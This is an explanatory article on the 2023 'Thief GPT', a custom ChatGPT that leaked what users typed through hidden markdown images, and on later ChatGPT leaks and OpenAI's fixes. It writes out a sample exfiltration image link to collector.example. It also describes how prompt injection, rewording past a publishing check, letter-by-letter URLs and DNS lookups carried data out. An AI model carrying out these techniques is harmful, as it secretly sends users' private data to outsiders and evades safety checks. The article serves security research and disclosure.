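# Johann Rehberger's "Thief GPT": a custom ChatGPT that secretly sent user data to an outside server

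## How ChatGPT could leak a conversation through an image, before November 2023

In November 2023, the security researcher Johann Rehberger built Thief GPT, a customised version of OpenAI's chatbot ChatGPT, to show that such versions could steal data from their users. It offered a game of tic-tac-toe, asked for an email address and a password, and secretly sent what the user typed to a server that Rehberger controlled. He made it public on 12 December 2023 in *Malicious ChatGPT Agents*, a post on his blog, Embrace The Red.

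The Thief GPT sent data out through an image that loaded in the chat window. Rehberger had reported this method to OpenAI seven months before he built the GPT.

### How a picture carries text out

The language model behind ChatGPT produces plain text. The chat window reads that text as Markdown, a notation that uses punctuation marks to indicate headings, bold type and pictures. A picture is written as `![description](web address)`. The chat window converts this into the web-page code for an image, and the user's browser fetches the picture from that address without the user having to click on anything.

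That fetch is the leak. To get a picture, a browser sends the server the full address, and an address has room for more than a location. Whatever follows a question mark is free text for the site's owner to use, and ordinary sites put things like search terms there. Suppose a user has typed "Dinner at eight" and the model has instructions to attach the user's last message to the address of a picture. It writes:

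`![dot](https://collector.example/dot.png?m=Dinner%20at%20eight)`

Each `%20` stands for a space, which a web address cannot contain. The browser requests `/dot.png?m=Dinner%20at%20eight` from `collector.example`. The server sends back a picture and records the request in its log, as web servers routinely do. Whoever runs the server can then read the message there.

Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* reproduces log lines from September 2023. A typical line includes the time to the second, the full address containing the stolen data, and the user's browser and operating system (Firefox 117 on a Mac).

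The user may see nothing, because the server can return a transparent image one pixel wide. The rest of ChatGPT's reply looks normal. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) similarly explains that websites commonly log the addresses people request, and that a user may never notice a background request, such as the loading of an embedded image.

ChatGPT's chat window fetched images from any address, so an attacker only needed a way to get the model to write the attacker's address with the user's words attached.

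### Prompt injection

To get a chatbot to send them a user's messages, attackers usually use prompt injection, in which a language model treats text from an untrusted source as instructions. This works because the model receives the operator's instructions, the user's question and any web page the user wants summarised as one run of text. An instruction hidden in the web page can therefore override the rest.

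In *Trust No AI*, Rehberger (2024) traces the discovery of prompt injection to a team at Preamble, which reported it to OpenAI in May 2022. The software developer Simon Willison named it that September. Rehberger compares it with SQL injection, an older attack that smuggles commands into a database through a form field. Programmers have precise guidance for preventing SQL injection but none for prompt injection, and Rehberger knows of no fix that works every time. If nobody can reliably stop the model from obeying the wrong text, the next best defense is to make sure it has no way to send anything out, which is why the image matters so much.

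In the early examples, people mostly attacked their own chatbot session. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, showed that the attacker need not be in the conversation. In an attack they called indirect prompt injection, the attacker plants instructions where the model is likely to read them, such as on a web page. For example, Microsoft's Bing Chat could read whatever page the user had open in the Edge browser, and text on that page steered the model even when the user couldn't see it. They listed stealing personal data and leaking chat sessions among the likely uses.

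### The two findings of spring 2023

The software engineer Roman Samoilenko combined prompt injection with the image leak in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. In his attack, the victim copies a passage from the attacker's website. A script on the page detects this and adds a hidden prompt to the clipboard. The victim then pastes the text into ChatGPT without reading it all. The prompt instructs ChatGPT to end its answer with a transparent one-pixel image whose address contains data from the chat. A more elaborate version instructs ChatGPT to add such an image to every later answer too, so the attacker also receives each new question the victim types.

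In one trial, Samoilenko asked ChatGPT to repair a piece of code, and the repaired login function reached his server inside an image address. But ChatGPT's answers vary from one run to the next, and his prompts sometimes failed. He found it easy to extract a user's earlier prompts or code but very difficult to extract passwords or access keys on their own, although the login function he extracted had a password written in it. When ChatGPT was slow, a victim might also see the strange line appear. Samoilenko considered this a set of tricks rather than the exploitation of a vulnerability, and he agreed that users should check what they paste. He still thought OpenAI should stop ChatGPT from replying with markdown images.

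On 14 April, Willison (2023) spread the news on his blog in a short notice, *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, which used Samoilenko's title. He called the method ingenious.

Rehberger found the leak independently a few days after Samoilenko, who had found it at the end of March. Rehberger's version did not require the user to paste anything. By then ChatGPT could use plugins, outside services that fetched web pages or looked up flights for it. Rehberger showed in *ChatGPT Plugins* that if a user asked about a malicious page and a plugin fetched it, the page could take over the session, have the model summarise the conversation so far, and send the summary to an outside server in an image address. In his demonstration, the text that reached the server included "TooManySecrets123", which the user had typed earlier in the chat.

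Rehberger reported the image leak to OpenAI on 9 April 2023. By his account, he pointed out in the exchange that followed that plugins would let attackers use the leak remotely, and OpenAI then told him that this was a feature and that it planned no changes. In later posts he gives the formal verdict as "won't fix". The trade publication SecurityWeek repeated the "feature" answer in December, but the details come from Rehberger, who does not record what reasoning, if any, OpenAI offered. OpenAI might understandably have dismissed Samoilenko's version, in which the victim has to paste in the attack, but its answer is much harder to defend for the plugin version, which Rehberger had raised before OpenAI gave that answer. In Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*, he rated the severity "High" on the standard industry scale.

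The leak became more useful to attackers as OpenAI added features such as plugins, which could reach data outside the chat. In *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen*, Willison described a Rehberger demonstration in which instructions on a web page made ChatGPT fetch the user's latest email from Gmail, summarise it in 20 words and attach the summary to a web address. The demonstration used a browsing plugin instead of an image to load the address, but it sent the data out in the same way, as part of the address.

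Plugins also made it easier to leak long conversations, which are awkward to fit in a web address. In September 2023, Rehberger had ChatGPT use a plugin to turn the whole conversation into a document or video stored online, so the image's address had to contain only the link. Asking ChatGPT to "backup" the conversation triggered extra confirmation requests, but it went ahead when he changed the word to "document". He sent OpenAI a draft of this work on 23 September and got an automated response.

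Rehberger's closest precursor to Thief GPT used Custom Instructions, a setting OpenAI introduced in July 2023 that adds a user's standing preferences to every exchange. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Custom Instructions* showed that an attacker could add instructions for the image leak there once and have them run in every chat, much as an intruder in an email account sets up a forwarding rule.

### What Microsoft, Google and Anthropic did

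Makers of other chatbots treated the same flaw as a vulnerability. Rehberger reported it to Microsoft on 8 April 2023, a day before he reported it to OpenAI, and on 15 June Microsoft told him it had a fix in place. According to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, at least part of that fix was a Content Security Policy, a rule that a website sends with a page to tell the browser where it may load content from. Microsoft's policy allowed images from four Bing addresses. Browsers have broadly supported such rules for images since August 2016, according to MDN's *CSP*, a reference page for web developers.

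A list like this closes the leak because the browser enforces it. An injected prompt can still make the model write the line with `collector.example` in it, but that domain is not on the list, so the browser never sends the request and nothing reaches the attacker's log. The drawback is that the chat window can no longer show images from sites that are not on the list.

The list of allowed domains also has to be narrow. Google's Bard already had such a list when Rehberger tested it in September 2023 with help from Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake, but it allowed images from any domain ending in google.com or googleusercontent.com. Anyone can run small programs, called Apps Scripts, on those same domains. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how Rehberger wrote a script that copied whatever followed the question mark in its web address into a Google Doc, which let him collect a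 user's chat history through a domain on the list. He reported this on 19 September, and Google confirmed a fix on 19 October. The list had not changed and images still appeared, so he guessed that Google had started filtering data out of the addresses.

The same mistake appeared years later in Superhuman AI, an email assistant. The security firm PromptArmor found that its list of allowed sites included docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms. *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* (Willison, 2026) explains that a Google Form will store data that arrives in an image request, so an attacker's form could collect the contents of a user's inbox. OpenAI has since questioned lists of trusted sites because a trusted site may redirect the request elsewhere, and because strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them. Those objections are fair for an assistant that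 has to browse the whole web, but they are weaker against a short list like the one Microsoft used, which governs only the images in a chat window.

Anthropic handled the problem differently in Claude. Rehberger's attack on Claude hid its instructions in a file that the user uploaded. He reported it on 12 July 2023, and Anthropic closed the report on 26 July. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* says that Claude stopped loading images automatically and showed a "Show Image" button instead. Rehberger thought this fix was imperfect because a user could still click the button, but the attack could no longer work silently.

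Google reacted fastest, to a similar flaw in its Vertex AI service for developers. According to Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI*, Google confirmed in 22 minutes that the flaw was a security issue and that it would fix it. ChatGPT kept loading images from any address until December 2023, when OpenAI added a check called url_safe on image addresses, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*.

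### Custom GPTs

The leak was therefore still open on 6 November 2023, when OpenAI's *Introducing GPTs* (2023) announced that people could make their own versions of ChatGPT and share them. OpenAI named these GPTs; most people say custom GPTs. Making one took no programming. The person or company setting it up, the builder, could give it:

- instructions, in plain language, on how to behave;
- knowledge, meaning extra material for it to draw on, such as uploaded files;
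- capabilities, such as searching the web, making images or analysing data;
- Actions, which connect it to outside services of the builder's choosing and which grew out of the earlier plugins.

One of OpenAI's own examples was a GPT that helps people learn the rules of board games.

At launch, using or building a custom GPT required a ChatGPT Plus account, which cost $20 a month and had a waiting list, according to the workplace publication Charter. Willison (2023), in *Exploring GPTs*, likewise described custom GPTs as chatbots that Plus users could make for other Plus subscribers. Companies on the Enterprise plan could also build GPTs for internal use. A public catalogue, the GPT Store, followed in January 2024.

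In the announcement, OpenAI also promised that "Your chats with GPTs are not shared with builders." If a GPT used an outside service, the user would choose whether data could go there. As of late 2026, OpenAI's help page *GPTs in ChatGPT* still says that builders cannot view individual conversations.

This was accurate about what OpenAI itself gave builders, who had no page for reading other people's chats. But ChatGPT would fetch an image from any address, so a builder with a server could still receive chat data through the image request. The promised choice about outside services did not prevent this, because a markdown image loaded without asking the user. A dishonest builder also did not need prompt injection. Samoilenko had to sneak his instructions in through the clipboard and Rehberger through a web page, and both sets of instructions went against what the user had asked for. A custom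 GPT had a box for the builder's instructions, which ChatGPT was supposed to follow.

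## The Thief GPT: how it was built, what it took and how it was published

Rehberger's December post on Embrace The Red has screenshots and a video of the Thief GPT but few details about its setup. He explained more of the setup later that month in a talk at the Chaos Communication Congress, an annual hacker conference in Hamburg. Embrace The Red's *37th Chaos Communication Congress* (2023) links to the talk's video and slides, and C3Subtitles (2024), a group that subtitles the congress's talks, hosts a rough transcript.

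### The game and the hidden image

In his instructions, Rehberger named the GPT Mallory, the Byte Bandit, and told it to play tic-tac-toe with the user. It was to ask for the user's email address first, ask for a password on the second turn, and send what the user typed to his server at every turn. He wrote the malicious part of the instructions in German and the rest in English. He did not explain why, but his slides, *New Important Instructions* (2023), list switching languages as one way to confuse a model.

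The player saw an ordinary game with a sign-in step. According to SecurityWeek, the GPT requested the player's email address for a "personalized experience" and the password as part of a "security process". In the text of his post, Rehberger says only that the GPT asked for personal information to ensure a good experience.

After each answer, ChatGPT added a markdown image with the user's words in its address. The address looked roughly like one that Embrace The Red reproduced later in December, which ended in `?thief=johannr@example.org`. Rehberger gave the image no description, so the chat window had nothing to display in its place and the line vanished as soon as it loaded.

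An audience member in Hamburg asked whether an attacker could hide even that brief flash of the address. Rehberger replied that this depended on the app. ChatGPT usually displayed its answers piece by piece, so a user who watched closely might glimpse the address, though it often went by too fast. The latest version had also stopped scrolling automatically, so in a long chat the address could appear and vanish below the visible part of the page.

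At the password step, ChatGPT objected that it could not ask for passwords and personal information, but only after Rehberger had typed something in. The text reached his server anyway. Whatever training led the model to object had changed its visible reply but had not stopped it from writing the image that carried the text.

Rehberger had switched off everything a builder could, so the GPT could not browse the web, run code or make pictures, and it had no Actions. In the talk he called this the most isolated way to build a GPT. A user who checked its capabilities would have concluded that it could not send data anywhere. He gave the example of a GPT for health questions, which people might trust with private details for that reason.

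Another audience member asked why he used images instead of having the chatbot visit the attacker's web address directly. Rehberger answered that by then ChatGPT sometimes asked the user to allow or deny such a visit, especially when a custom GPT used Actions, but it loaded images without asking.

TechRadar's *OpenAI says it has fixed a potentially serious ChatGPT flaw* reported that malicious chatbots could also take "metadata and technical data", which Rehberger's post does not mention. The claim is partly right, since any image request gives the server the time and the type of browser. TechRadar also wrote that OpenAI had not responded to Rehberger. This is wrong, because OpenAI had closed his ticket as "Not Applicable" before ignoring two follow-ups.

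### Getting past the publishing check

A new GPT was private by default ("Only me"), but its builder could open it to anyone with a link or make it public. When Rehberger first tried to share the Thief GPT, he got an error message, apparently because it had failed OpenAI's "brand and usage" guidelines. He noted that this first version contained words such as "steal" and "malicious".

Rehberger changed the wording and the GPT passed, so anyone could now use it. He also read on OpenAI's page that a fully public GPT might appear in the GPT Store. He did not want the Thief GPT listed there, so he switched it back to link-only sharing. He reported it to OpenAI on 13 November, a week after OpenAI announced custom GPTs.

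OpenAI had said in that announcement that new systems would help it review GPTs against its usage policies, to stop people from sharing harmful ones, including those involving "fraudulent activity". A game built to collect passwords clearly fits that description, but changing a few words was enough to get it past the review.

Rehberger was "pretty sure" that a language model did the checking. If so, he reasoned, dubious instructions might sometimes pass by chance, and changing any few characters might be enough to get them through. He reported no repeated trials to test this guess. A later OpenAI help page, *How we identify problematic content on our services for individuals*, mentions automated tools such as its moderation service, which detects potentially harmful text, but this does not establish what OpenAI was using in November 2023.

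According to the same page, a builder whose GPT fails can edit out the problematic content or appeal. This is reasonable for an honest builder who tripped a filter by accident, but it also lets a dishonest builder remove the suspicious words and keep the behaviour.

Rehberger concluded that getting around the check was "trivial", based on one GPT that failed it and then passed after a small edit. This shows that the check could not be relied on, but not how many malicious GPTs it stopped.

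OpenAI's written rules became more specific after the demonstration. *OpenAI introduces acceptable uses for API and custom GPTs* (Bai, 2024) reported that the policy of 10 January 2024 prohibited builders from asking users for sensitive identifiers and from misrepresenting a GPT's purpose.

### Dishonest builders and prompt injection

The attacker in the Thief GPT is its builder, rather than an outsider as in indirect prompt injection. The two attacks are easy to confuse because both can use the image leak, and Rehberger presented the Thief GPT in a talk that was mostly about indirect prompt injection.

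In his slides, Rehberger sorts threats into three kinds: a flawed model, a user who attacks the model, and a third party who attacks through prompt injection. A dishonest builder does not fit neatly into any of these.

In 2026, Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* described two ways an attacker could exploit a different leak. The attacker could persuade the user to paste in a malicious prompt disguised as a trick for unlocking premium features, or build the attack into a custom GPT. Check Point considered the custom GPT even more dangerous, because the user doesn't have to paste in anything suspicious and only has to open the GPT and start talking.

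The two attacks call for partly different defences:

| Defence | Against a dishonest builder | Against prompt injection |
|---|---|---|
| Checking a GPT's instructions before sharing | Helps if the check spots the malicious ones | No help, because the GPT's own instructions are honest |
| Verifying builders' identities and letting users report GPTs | Helps once somebody notices the theft | Little help, because the builder is innocent |
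| Screening web pages and files for hidden instructions | No help, because the builder does not need any | Helps, but misses some attacks |
| Loading images only from a short list of trusted sites | Blocks the image leak | Blocks the image leak |
| Asking the user before a tool sends data out | Helps, unless the user trusts the GPT and agrees | Helps if the user reads the request |

Limiting what data can leave the chat works against both attacks because it does not depend on recognising bad instructions. The measures Rehberger recommended in his 2024 paper included refusing to show images or links from untrusted domains and telling the user, before a tool acts, what it will do and with what data.

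A custom GPT built without malicious intent can also be vulnerable to prompt injection, for example if it browses the web and reads a malicious page. Even if OpenAI reviewed such a GPT perfectly, the attack could still happen.

### "Confide in Claire"

On 29 November 2023, about two weeks before Rehberger published his demonstration, two other researchers described a similar one in *Navigating the Hidden Risks of Custom GPT Configurations*. Their GPT, "Confide in Claire", encouraged people to talk about what was bothering them. It drew out sensitive information and, when the conversation ended, sent a summary to a server that one of the researchers controlled.

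Claire did not use images. It relied on two tools that OpenAI supplied with ChatGPT:

1. The GPT waited for a phrase that people use to sign off, such as "thank you" or "goodbye".
2. Code Interpreter, which runs small programs, converted the summary into base64. This is a standard way of writing any data as a string of letters, digits and a few symbols. It looks like gibberish, but anyone can convert it back.
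3. The browsing tool, Browse with Bing, opened a web address on the researcher's server that contained the encoded summary.

The GPT waited for the farewell to send the data, when the user was about to stop paying attention. Once the tools finished, ChatGPT also hid the details of what they had done. This was meant to keep the chat tidy, but it left few traces of the theft.

The researchers then built a second GPT, "Senior Dev Reviewer", which offered to review code and sent whatever the user entered to an outside server in the same way. This GPT could worry companies more than the first, since a programmer might paste in proprietary code without thinking of it as personal information. *Demonstrate new attack vector for GPTs feature (PITM)* describes a similar GPT, "Python Engineer", which encoded the user's prompts and sent them to an outside address.

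These demonstrations showed that a GPT could also leak data without images. Claire would still have worked if OpenAI had fixed only the image leak. But Claire needed browsing and Code Interpreter, so a wary user could have seen that it had access to the web, a clue that the Thief GPT did not give.

Claire's builders also found that the publishing check blocked most plainly written malicious instructions, but they could get past it by disguising the text or adding a suffix designed to defeat it. They found no limit on how many times a builder could try.

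If Rehberger was right that chance plays a part, unlimited attempts make the check much easier to get past. Suppose each reworded version of a malicious GPT had an independent 5% chance of passing. The probability that at least one of 20 versions would pass is 1 − 0.95²⁰, or about 64%. The real rate is unknown, but even a fairly good check gives weak protection if someone can keep trying without penalty.

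The researchers reported their findings through Bugcrowd, a platform for reporting security flaws. They received the same verdict as Rehberger, "Not Applicable", on the grounds that model safety was outside the platform's scope.

### Whether people would hand over their details

All of these GPTs were proofs of concept. In December, Rehberger demonstrated the Thief GPT live on another person, whom Embrace The Red calls a "consenting victim". His server received the details of the conversation, and the victim was "not too amused". Rehberger reported no victims who had not consented, and he did not measure how many players would type in a real password.

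The nearest evidence comes from a randomised trial with 502 participants, *Malicious LLM-Based Conversational AI Makes Users Reveal Personal Information* (Zhan, Carrillo and colleagues, 2025). Each participant talked to one of 12 chatbots without being told beforehand that some were designed to extract personal data. The chatbots used three openly available models and four sets of instructions. One set was harmless, and the other three told the chatbot to ask for personal details outright, to help the user first and then ask, or to ask while offering sympathy and sharing stories.

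The researchers needed only written instructions to make the chatbots malicious, as with a custom GPT. The models refused direct requests to collect personal information, but complied when given a role, such as a detective building a profile.

Most people answered, and in the two most successful versions, 39 of 40 and 40 of 43 participants disclosed something personal. When the researchers offered a separate group of 50 people an optional form instead, only 12 gave any information.

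The sympathetic chatbots collected less information than the blunter ones, but it was more often true. Participants trusted the sympathetic chatbots about as much as the harmless ones. People who used the blunter chatbots complained of irrelevant questions and sometimes made up their answers. The researchers confirmed that 40 of the participants they checked had given false details, and 33 of those had used one of the two blunter kinds.

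By this measure, Claire was probably the better-designed trap. Nobody needs a password to play tic-tac-toe, and some players would presumably have made one up. Personal questions make obvious sense in a GPT that invites people to talk about their troubles.

The trial provides much less evidence about passwords. Participants most often disclosed their age, hobbies and country, and Zhan and colleagues give no figure for passwords. People who share their hobbies with a chatbot may still be unwilling to give it their email password. The participants were also in a paid university study, which may have made them more trusting.

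## OpenAI's response, and the leaks found after its fix, 2023 to 2026

Rehberger reported the Thief GPT and its instructions to OpenAI on 13 November 2023, and OpenAI closed the ticket as "Not Applicable" on 15 November. He followed up twice, got no reply, and published the demonstration on Embrace The Red on 12 December.

The attack kept working for about another week, including in Rehberger's live demonstration on a consenting victim. The morning after the demonstration, around 20 December, he found that ChatGPT's website had started checking image addresses before loading them. The timing suggests that the publicity helped, although OpenAI may already have been working on the check when he published.

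### What "Not Applicable" meant

On 11 April 2023, two days after Rehberger first reported the image leak, OpenAI (2023) announced a bug bounty, a programme that pays outsiders $200 to $20,000 for reporting security flaws. The company Bugcrowd managed the submissions. Rehberger does not name the platform that handled his Thief GPT ticket, but the verdict he received, "Not Applicable", is one of Bugcrowd's standard verdicts.

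Bugcrowd's *Understanding substates* defines this label as meaning that a report "does not apply to the target or application". Bugcrowd has separate labels for reports that break a programme's rules ("Out of Scope") and for real problems that a company has decided to accept ("Informational"). Taken literally, the label is a strange one for the Thief GPT, which ran inside ChatGPT, a product the bounty covered. Reviewers seem to have used the label loosely. For example, the builders of "Confide in Claire" received it with the explanation that model safety was out of scope.

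From the start, OpenAI's bug bounty program did not reward reports about the "content of model prompts and responses" unless they had a "directly verifiable security impact" on a service the program covered, according to TechTarget's *OpenAI launches bug bounty program with Bugcrowd*. OpenAI reasoned that model safety problems are not "individual, discrete bugs that can be directly fixed", and it asked researchers to report them through a separate form. The program also excluded social engineering, meaning attacks that work by deceiving a person.

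Under these rules, OpenAI had a case for rejecting the Thief GPT. A game that asks for a password is much like a phishing page, a fake site that collects logins. Web hosting companies usually take such a page down and perhaps ban whoever made it, rather than treat it as a bug in their software. No single code change would stop builders from writing dishonest instructions, so this part of Rehberger's report fits OpenAI's description of a model safety problem.

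The image request differs from a phishing page, where people hand their details directly to the page's owner. Someone playing tic-tac-toe in ChatGPT was typing into OpenAI's product, and OpenAI had promised that builders would not see the chats. ChatGPT's own chat window then sent the text to the builder without asking the user. Anyone could verify the leak in the server's log, so the report arguably met the rules' exception for a verifiable security impact. The leak was also a discrete bug that OpenAI could fix directly, as it showed by shipping a partial fix five weeks after closing the ticket. OpenAI could have sent the dishonest game to the people who handle abuse and still accepted the image leak as a security flaw.

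A later report of a similar flaw got the same answer. In *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, the computer scientist Gregory Schwartzman (2024) found that instructions hidden in pasted text could make ChatGPT reveal a user's personal details through the web addresses it opened. He writes that he reported this through Bugcrowd and that the issue was "deemed non applicable". He then tried MITRE, which helps run the public catalogue of software flaws. MITRE found the report very interesting but could not give it a catalogue number, because ChatGPT is a web application that customers do not control. IPA, a Japanese government-backed agency, told him that OpenAI's terms of use prevented it from acting.

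TechTarget reported that OpenAI's bug bounty programme forbade researchers from publicly disclosing the vulnerabilities they submitted. Katie Moussouris, founder of the security firm Luta Security, called the rule "shortsighted" and argued that the public should hear about risks a company chooses not to fix. The Thief GPT supports her argument, since people learned of the risk only because Rehberger published a report that OpenAI had turned down.

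On 25 March 2026, OpenAI launched a second bug bounty programme, the Safety Bug Bounty, for problems that can cause harm without meeting the definition of a security vulnerability (OpenAI, 2026). It covers cases where an attacker's text takes over a victim's AI agent and makes it leak sensitive information, provided the attack works at least half the time. Jailbreaks, which get a model to break its own content rules, remain out of scope. The older security bounty continues and had rewarded 409 vulnerabilities by the time the new programme launched, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *OpenAI Expands Bug Bounty to Cover AI Abuse and 'Safety' Concerns*.

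Rehberger's web-page attacks would clearly fit the new category. The Thief GPT fits less well, because nobody hijacked it. But OpenAI also considers other flaws case by case if they lead directly to user harm and have a specific fix. The image leak meets that description, but a GPT that only asks for a password and stores nothing outside the chat probably does not.

### How url_safe works

The check that appeared in December 2023 is called url_safe. Suppose ChatGPT writes an image line whose address is `https://collector.example/dot.png?m=Dinner%20at%20eight`. In the version Rehberger examined, the following happened:

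1. The chat window recognised the line as an image but did not fetch it yet.
2. It sent the full address to an OpenAI server and asked whether the address was safe.
3. The server returned a verdict, such as `{"safe":false}`.
4. If the verdict was false, the chat window left the picture out and the browser never contacted `collector.example`. If it was true, the picture loaded as before.

Microsoft used a fixed list of image sources for Bing Chat, which any researcher could read. OpenAI's server instead checked each address against unpublished rules. This let ChatGPT keep showing pictures from many sites and gave OpenAI a central record of suspicious addresses, which Rehberger thought could help the company spot attacks. But outsiders could only guess at the rules by testing them. Rehberger wondered whether the server looked addresses up in Bing's search index, and he hoped that a language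 model was not making the decision alone.

Rehberger's first tests, described on Embrace The Red, showed that the check still let some data through. He made a separate image address for each letter and digit, 36 in all, and nine of them passed. The check accepted the address ending in `a.png` but rejected the one ending in `d.png`, and he could see no reason for the difference. Using characters that passed, he sent the word "hi" to his server as two image requests.

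An attacker could therefore still get data out, but only in tiny pieces. Stealing data now took a series of invisible images instead of one, which was slower and easier for the user or OpenAI to notice. Rehberger suggested limiting each reply to one image or a handful, which would have slowed this method further. The attacker had only nine characters to work with, but could encode the missing letters as combinations of those nine.

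The iOS app had no check. In the chat window, the check began by sending each address to OpenAI's server, so OpenAI had to add that step to every app separately. Rehberger recommended running the check entirely on the server, where it would protect all the apps at once.

On 21 December, Willison called the fix "half-baked". He found it odd that OpenAI had not blocked images from outside sites, and he expected a creative attacker to get past the filter by hiding data in other parts of the address, such as the file name. Rehberger, who had spent eight months trying to get OpenAI to act, was happy to see any fix and considered this one a step in the right direction. Both men expected workarounds, and researchers kept finding them for the next two years.

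### Apps without the check, and ChatGPT's memory

In 2024 OpenAI gave ChatGPT a memory, a set of notes about the user that it draws on in later conversations. In May of that year, Rehberger reported that a malicious web page could add false notes to this memory. OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue, not a security concern.

In June he sent OpenAI a stronger version, which combined a planted memory with the image leak. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* describes how a single question to ChatGPT about a malicious page let the page plant a memory with instructions for the leak. From then on, ChatGPT sent everything the user typed and all its own answers to Rehberger's server, including in new chats.

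This worked in ChatGPT's macOS app because OpenAI had released it without url_safe. The Android app had the same gap, as Rehberger had warned.

OpenAI fixed the macOS app in September 2024. The fix stopped data from leaking out through images, but web pages could still plant memories in ChatGPT, so Rehberger advised users to review their stored memories regularly.

OpenAI rejected the report of a planted memory alone, but fixed the attack once the memory was combined with a working data leak. It evidently treated planting information in ChatGPT's memory as a model safety issue and extracting data as a security issue. By that standard, OpenAI would have accepted the Thief GPT report in November 2023, at least the part about the image.

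### Trusted sites that attackers could use

In October 2024, Rehberger reported several ways around url_safe. Some domains always passed the check even though outsiders could rent storage on them and read the access logs. An attacker could have ChatGPT request an image from one of these domains and collect the user's data from the log. Google had made the same mistake with Bard a year earlier.

Some of these gaps were still open in August 2025, when Rehberger published *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* on Embrace The Red. By then ChatGPT could draw on a user's earlier conversations, so a malicious PDF or web page could make it send those out as well. Rehberger had asked OpenAI about the fix several times over the previous month but got no update. He wanted OpenAI to publish its list of safe domains and let business customers set their own.

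The security company Tenable had found a similar gap. According to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass*, url_safe approved every bing.com link. Bing's search results use bing.com links that forward visitors to other sites, so a link could pass the check and still lead to an attacker's page. Tenable reported the problem to OpenAI on 10 December 2024. Its timeline then lists six requests for an update, the last on 4 March 2025, and no substantive answer. The problem was unresolved when Tenable published its advisory.

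In November 2025, Tenable's *HackedGPT* described seven weaknesses in ChatGPT, including this one, and combined them into complete attacks. OpenAI had tried to protect users by having a second model read web pages without access to their memories or conversations. Tenable found that a malicious page could make this model include instructions in its answer. ChatGPT then read the answer as part of the conversation and followed the instructions. Tenable used this to extract private information from users' memories and chat histories, one letter at a time.

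Tenable reported that it had worked with OpenAI to fix some of the weaknesses but that several remained in GPT-5, which OpenAI had released that August. Rehberger gives a more favourable account in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, writing that OpenAI strengthened url_safe around August 2025 and that this stopped the attacks he had demonstrated. Both accounts can be true, since Tenable did most of its research on the older GPT-4o and gives no date for its GPT-5 tests.

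### ZombieAgent

OpenAI had also tried to stop ChatGPT from putting stolen data into web addresses. ChatGPT would open a link unchanged but refused to add anything to it. Zvika Babo, a researcher at the security company Radware, got around this in September 2025 by supplying a ready-made address for each letter and digit. ChatGPT could then spell out the stolen text by opening the right addresses in order. Rehberger had used the same basic idea in a December 2023 test that leaked the word "hi".

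Radware's *ZombieAgent*, published in January 2026, shows that attackers could steal much more by then, because users could connect ChatGPT to services such as Gmail, Outlook, Google Drive and GitHub. In the main attack, the attacker sent the victim an email with hidden instructions. When the victim later asked ChatGPT to do something in Gmail, ChatGPT read the email and sent private data to the attacker. Radware could also take information from chat history and memory. In another version, the attack collected addresses from the victim's inbox, and the attacker's server emailed the same instructions to each of them.

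OpenAI's own servers opened the links in this attack, so a list enforced by the user's browser, like Microsoft's, would not have stopped it.

Radware also submitted its report through Bugcrowd, as Schwartzman had, but it was better received. Bugcrowd reproduced the attack within four days and forwarded the report to OpenAI, which fixed the flaw on 16 December 2025. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, a January 2026 news report, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from opening links that came from emails, with exceptions such as those in a well-known public index.

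### OpenAI's rule for links in 2026

On 28 January 2026, OpenAI explained that its newer protections let ChatGPT open an address automatically only if that exact address was already public. OpenAI checks the address against an index built by a crawler, a program that explores the web much as a search engine does and has no access to anybody's chats. The address ending in `?m=Dinner%20at%20eight` would fail this check because it did not exist until a user typed those words. ChatGPT must then try another site or warn the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

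This was close to what Rehberger guessed in 2023, except that OpenAI uses its own index instead of Bing's. It is also a better test than checking whether a site is reputable, because an attacker can rent space on a trusted domain, but renting it does not make a newly invented address there public.

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection*, published on 11 March 2026, says that most attempts to steal data fail because OpenAI has trained ChatGPT to refuse. When the training fails, the check, which OpenAI now calls Safe Url, is supposed to detect that information from the conversation is about to go to a third party. OpenAI then either blocks the transfer or shows the user the information and asks for confirmation. The same check covers OpenAI's web browser, Atlas, and its research tool, Deep Research. OpenAI says sensitive information should not leave "silently or without appropriate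 safeguards". ChatGPT failed that standard in 2023, as the Thief GPT showed. The article cites a blog post that Rehberger published in the month he first reported the image leak.

OpenAI promises only that the address itself will not quietly give away a user's data. A page can still mislead the user or contain harmful instructions. Rehberger considered the change a significant improvement but noted that the letter-by-letter method still works if the attacker's addresses are already in the index. Anyone with a fairly large blog probably has 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit. OpenAI acknowledges this weakness in its technical paper. Rehberger suggested preventing ChatGPT from visiting the same address twice in a session, which would make longer messages harder to send.

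He also worried that some OpenAI developers might not know about the protection and might release features without it. The 2024 macOS and Android apps are good evidence for that concern.

A test at Soongsil University in Seoul suggests that the protection had gaps soon after OpenAI described it. In *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection*, Yang, Na and Choi (2026) report that on 3 February 2026 ChatGPT, running GPT-5.2, sent a made-up user's date of birth to the researchers' server in a web address. They present this as a proof of concept and give no success rate for the full attack.

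### A leak that needed no link

All these protections apply to web addresses that ChatGPT opens or displays. In early 2026, Check Point Research reported a leak that bypassed them through the tool ChatGPT uses to run code.

OpenAI had cut this tool off from the internet, and ordinary attempts to reach an outside server from it failed. But the tool could still look up domain names. Before a computer can contact a site such as `example.com`, it requests the site's numerical address from the domain name system, or DNS. The request passes through a chain of servers and can end at one run by the domain's owner. An attacker who owns a domain can therefore receive data written into the name being looked up, even if the computer never connects to the site.

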